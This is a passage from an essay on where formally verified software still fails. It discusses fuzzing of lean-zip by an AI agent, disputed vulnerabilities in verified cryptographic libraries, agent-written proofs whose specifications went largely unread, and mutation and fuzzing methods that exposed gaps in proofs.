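kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes an attempt to break it. The tester removed the theorems and documentation, so that the Claude agent doing the work wouldn't know the code was verified. In about 19 hours, the agent's fuzzers ran the program nearly 106 million times. They found no memory errors in the Lean code, but two bugs outside the proved part. The archive parser, which had no theorems, believed whatever size a file claimed for its contents and could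 run out of memory. The other bug was in Lean's runtime, which adds 24 bytes to each request for memory using 64-bit arithmetic. For the largest possible request, the sum wraps around.

$$
24+(2^{64}-1)\equiv 23 \pmod{2^{64}}
$$

The runtime would then reserve 23 bytes for far more data than that. Any Lean program that passed on such a request had the same problem.

The clean result for the Lean code may be due more to the language than to the theorem. The theorem covers only files that lean-zip itself compressed, but the fuzzers supplied damaged files. A compressor and decompressor that both returned their input unchanged would also satisfy the theorem, though they would presumably fail zlib's test suite.

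Critics of two cryptographic libraries, libcrux and hpke-rs, report a less favourable result. *Verification Theatre* (Kobeissi, 2026) presents 13 vulnerabilities that verification missed, nine of them in unverified code. One, a byte-order mistake, caused decryption failures in the messaging app Signal. By April, *The Verification Facade* (2026), from Kobeissi's firm, Symbolic Software, had listed 16 vulnerabilities across six projects, including wrong specifications, false proofs and unsound axioms. The libraries' maker had claimed that nobody had found a bug in the verified code. *We Found Bugs in CE Labs' Verified Code* (Symbolic Software, 2026) quotes and rejects that claim. Part of the disagreement may be about what "verified" means, because code can pass the verifier with a proof that rests on a false axiom, and such a proof gives no reason to trust the code.

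The other tests are easier to sort by place. The CompCert figures leave out crashes.

| Software | Proved code | Unproved code around it | Specification or hardware model | Verification tools or runtime |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Three distributed systems | 1 | 10 | 2 | 3 |
| CompCert | 0 | 6 | 2 | 0 |
| lean-zip | 0 | 1 | 0 | 1 |

The only bug in proved code was a stack overflow in Verdi, where the logic was correct. This supports the claim that proved code contains few bugs and that most bugs are at its boundaries. The table covers only five pieces of software and 26 bugs, too few to give reliable rates. Testers also tend to look where they expect faults. Fonseca and colleagues concentrated on source code and specifications, so they may have missed bugs in compilers and operating systems, and Kobeissi set out to examine the boundary of the proofs.

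### Larger kernels and unread specifications

AI agents have made proofs much faster to produce. The xv6 proof took 102 days, whereas seL4's took experts years. Kaashoek and Zeldovich still had to supply the overall plan and help design the intermediate specifications. Their prompts were about three times as long as their paper.

In *Zero-Trust Formal Methods*, Philipp (2026) delegated even more. Agents, mostly running Claude Opus 5.5, wrote verified checkers for the answers of automated solvers, programs that search for solutions or show that none exist. The agents produced about 87,000 lines of Rust, including proofs, and 45,000 lines for the proof assistant Isabelle. Nobody read the code or the proofs, but people reviewed about 2,500 lines of specification and a translation of similar length for a second verifier.

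Larger verified kernels therefore look practical to prove, but the amount people have to read hasn't fallen as quickly as the proof effort. The definitions behind xv6's console theorem are about 70% as long as the kernel. If people skim them, an error can go unnoticed, as happened with xv6's empty theorem about crash recovery and with the clause in PocketFlow's specification that applied to nothing.

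In Philipp's example, the agents wrote a formal description of a language that Verus, a verifier for Rust, uses internally. They also wrote a program to check Verus's translations against it. The description failed four of six reviews, although the agents' program reported complete success every time. In the fourth review, a reviewer found that two components read the same symbol differently, so a false proof could pass both.

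The agents' tests also gave too much confidence in the unverified code. Reviewers planted 18 errors in a parser that no person had read, and the tests missed 15, including three that could have led to false results. After the agents added 101 tests, the suite caught all 18.

These examples suggest that the risk moves into specifications and joining code. Having agents review each other's work helps, but most of Philipp's agents ran the same model and could miss the same errors. The results also come from the project's own author, so they are weaker evidence than an outside test.

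### Methods that found the gaps

Researchers found several of these faults by deliberately breaking a program and checking whether it still passed verification. Fonseca and colleagues built a tool that disables random pieces of IronFleet's code. Depending on the function, the tool needed between 18 and about 8,000 attempts on average to find a version that no longer filtered out repeated requests but still passed verification. They also proved that the specification allowed a counter built on IronFleet to reach any value after a single request to add to it. The specification was therefore incomplete, since no sensible user would want that behavior.

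In Philipp's project, verification rejected 396 of 492 altered programs. Many of the other 96 were harmless, including 32 that only made a checker reject more valid certificates, which the specification allows. But verification also had a serious gap, because it passed a program with swapped instructions for reporting success and failure, which printed "verified" for every certificate it rejected. The agents then extended the proof to cover the choice between the two instructions, and all 23 variants of this kind failed verification. In later tests with planted defects, the verified checkers rejected every false certificate, and the weaknesses were in the ordinary code and procedures that enforced the project's rules.

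Random comparison is useful even when a proof exists. For example, it uncovered Mashin's mismatched capability names. Cai and colleagues fed altered certificates to both Keel and the older checker it replaces, and two of the older checker's bugs were found only this way. They point out that fuzzing tests what Keel's proof assumes, such as whether the compiled C code behaves as their model of C predicts, though it can't strengthen the proof itself. Fuzzing also finds bugs in verification tools. *From Formal Methods to Fuzzing and Back* (2026) reports that it led developers to fix fifty bugs in Frama-C, a tool for analysing C programs, and exposed soundness bugs in commercial tools that engineers use to approve hardware designs.

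Testers can use a written list of assumptions to decide where to look. Philipp's project keeps one for each program, covering every axiom, skipped proof, trusted parser and output routine, and a script raises an error if the code and the list differ. Fonseca and colleagues tested assumptions directly, for example by checking whether Verdi's shim delivered messages intact, and their tools can detect 13 of the 16 bugs automatically. For an AI agent, the list should include the assumption that every route to the outside world passes through the kernel. In the incidents that OpenAI and Anthropic disclosed in 2026, some test environments had unintended routes to real systems.
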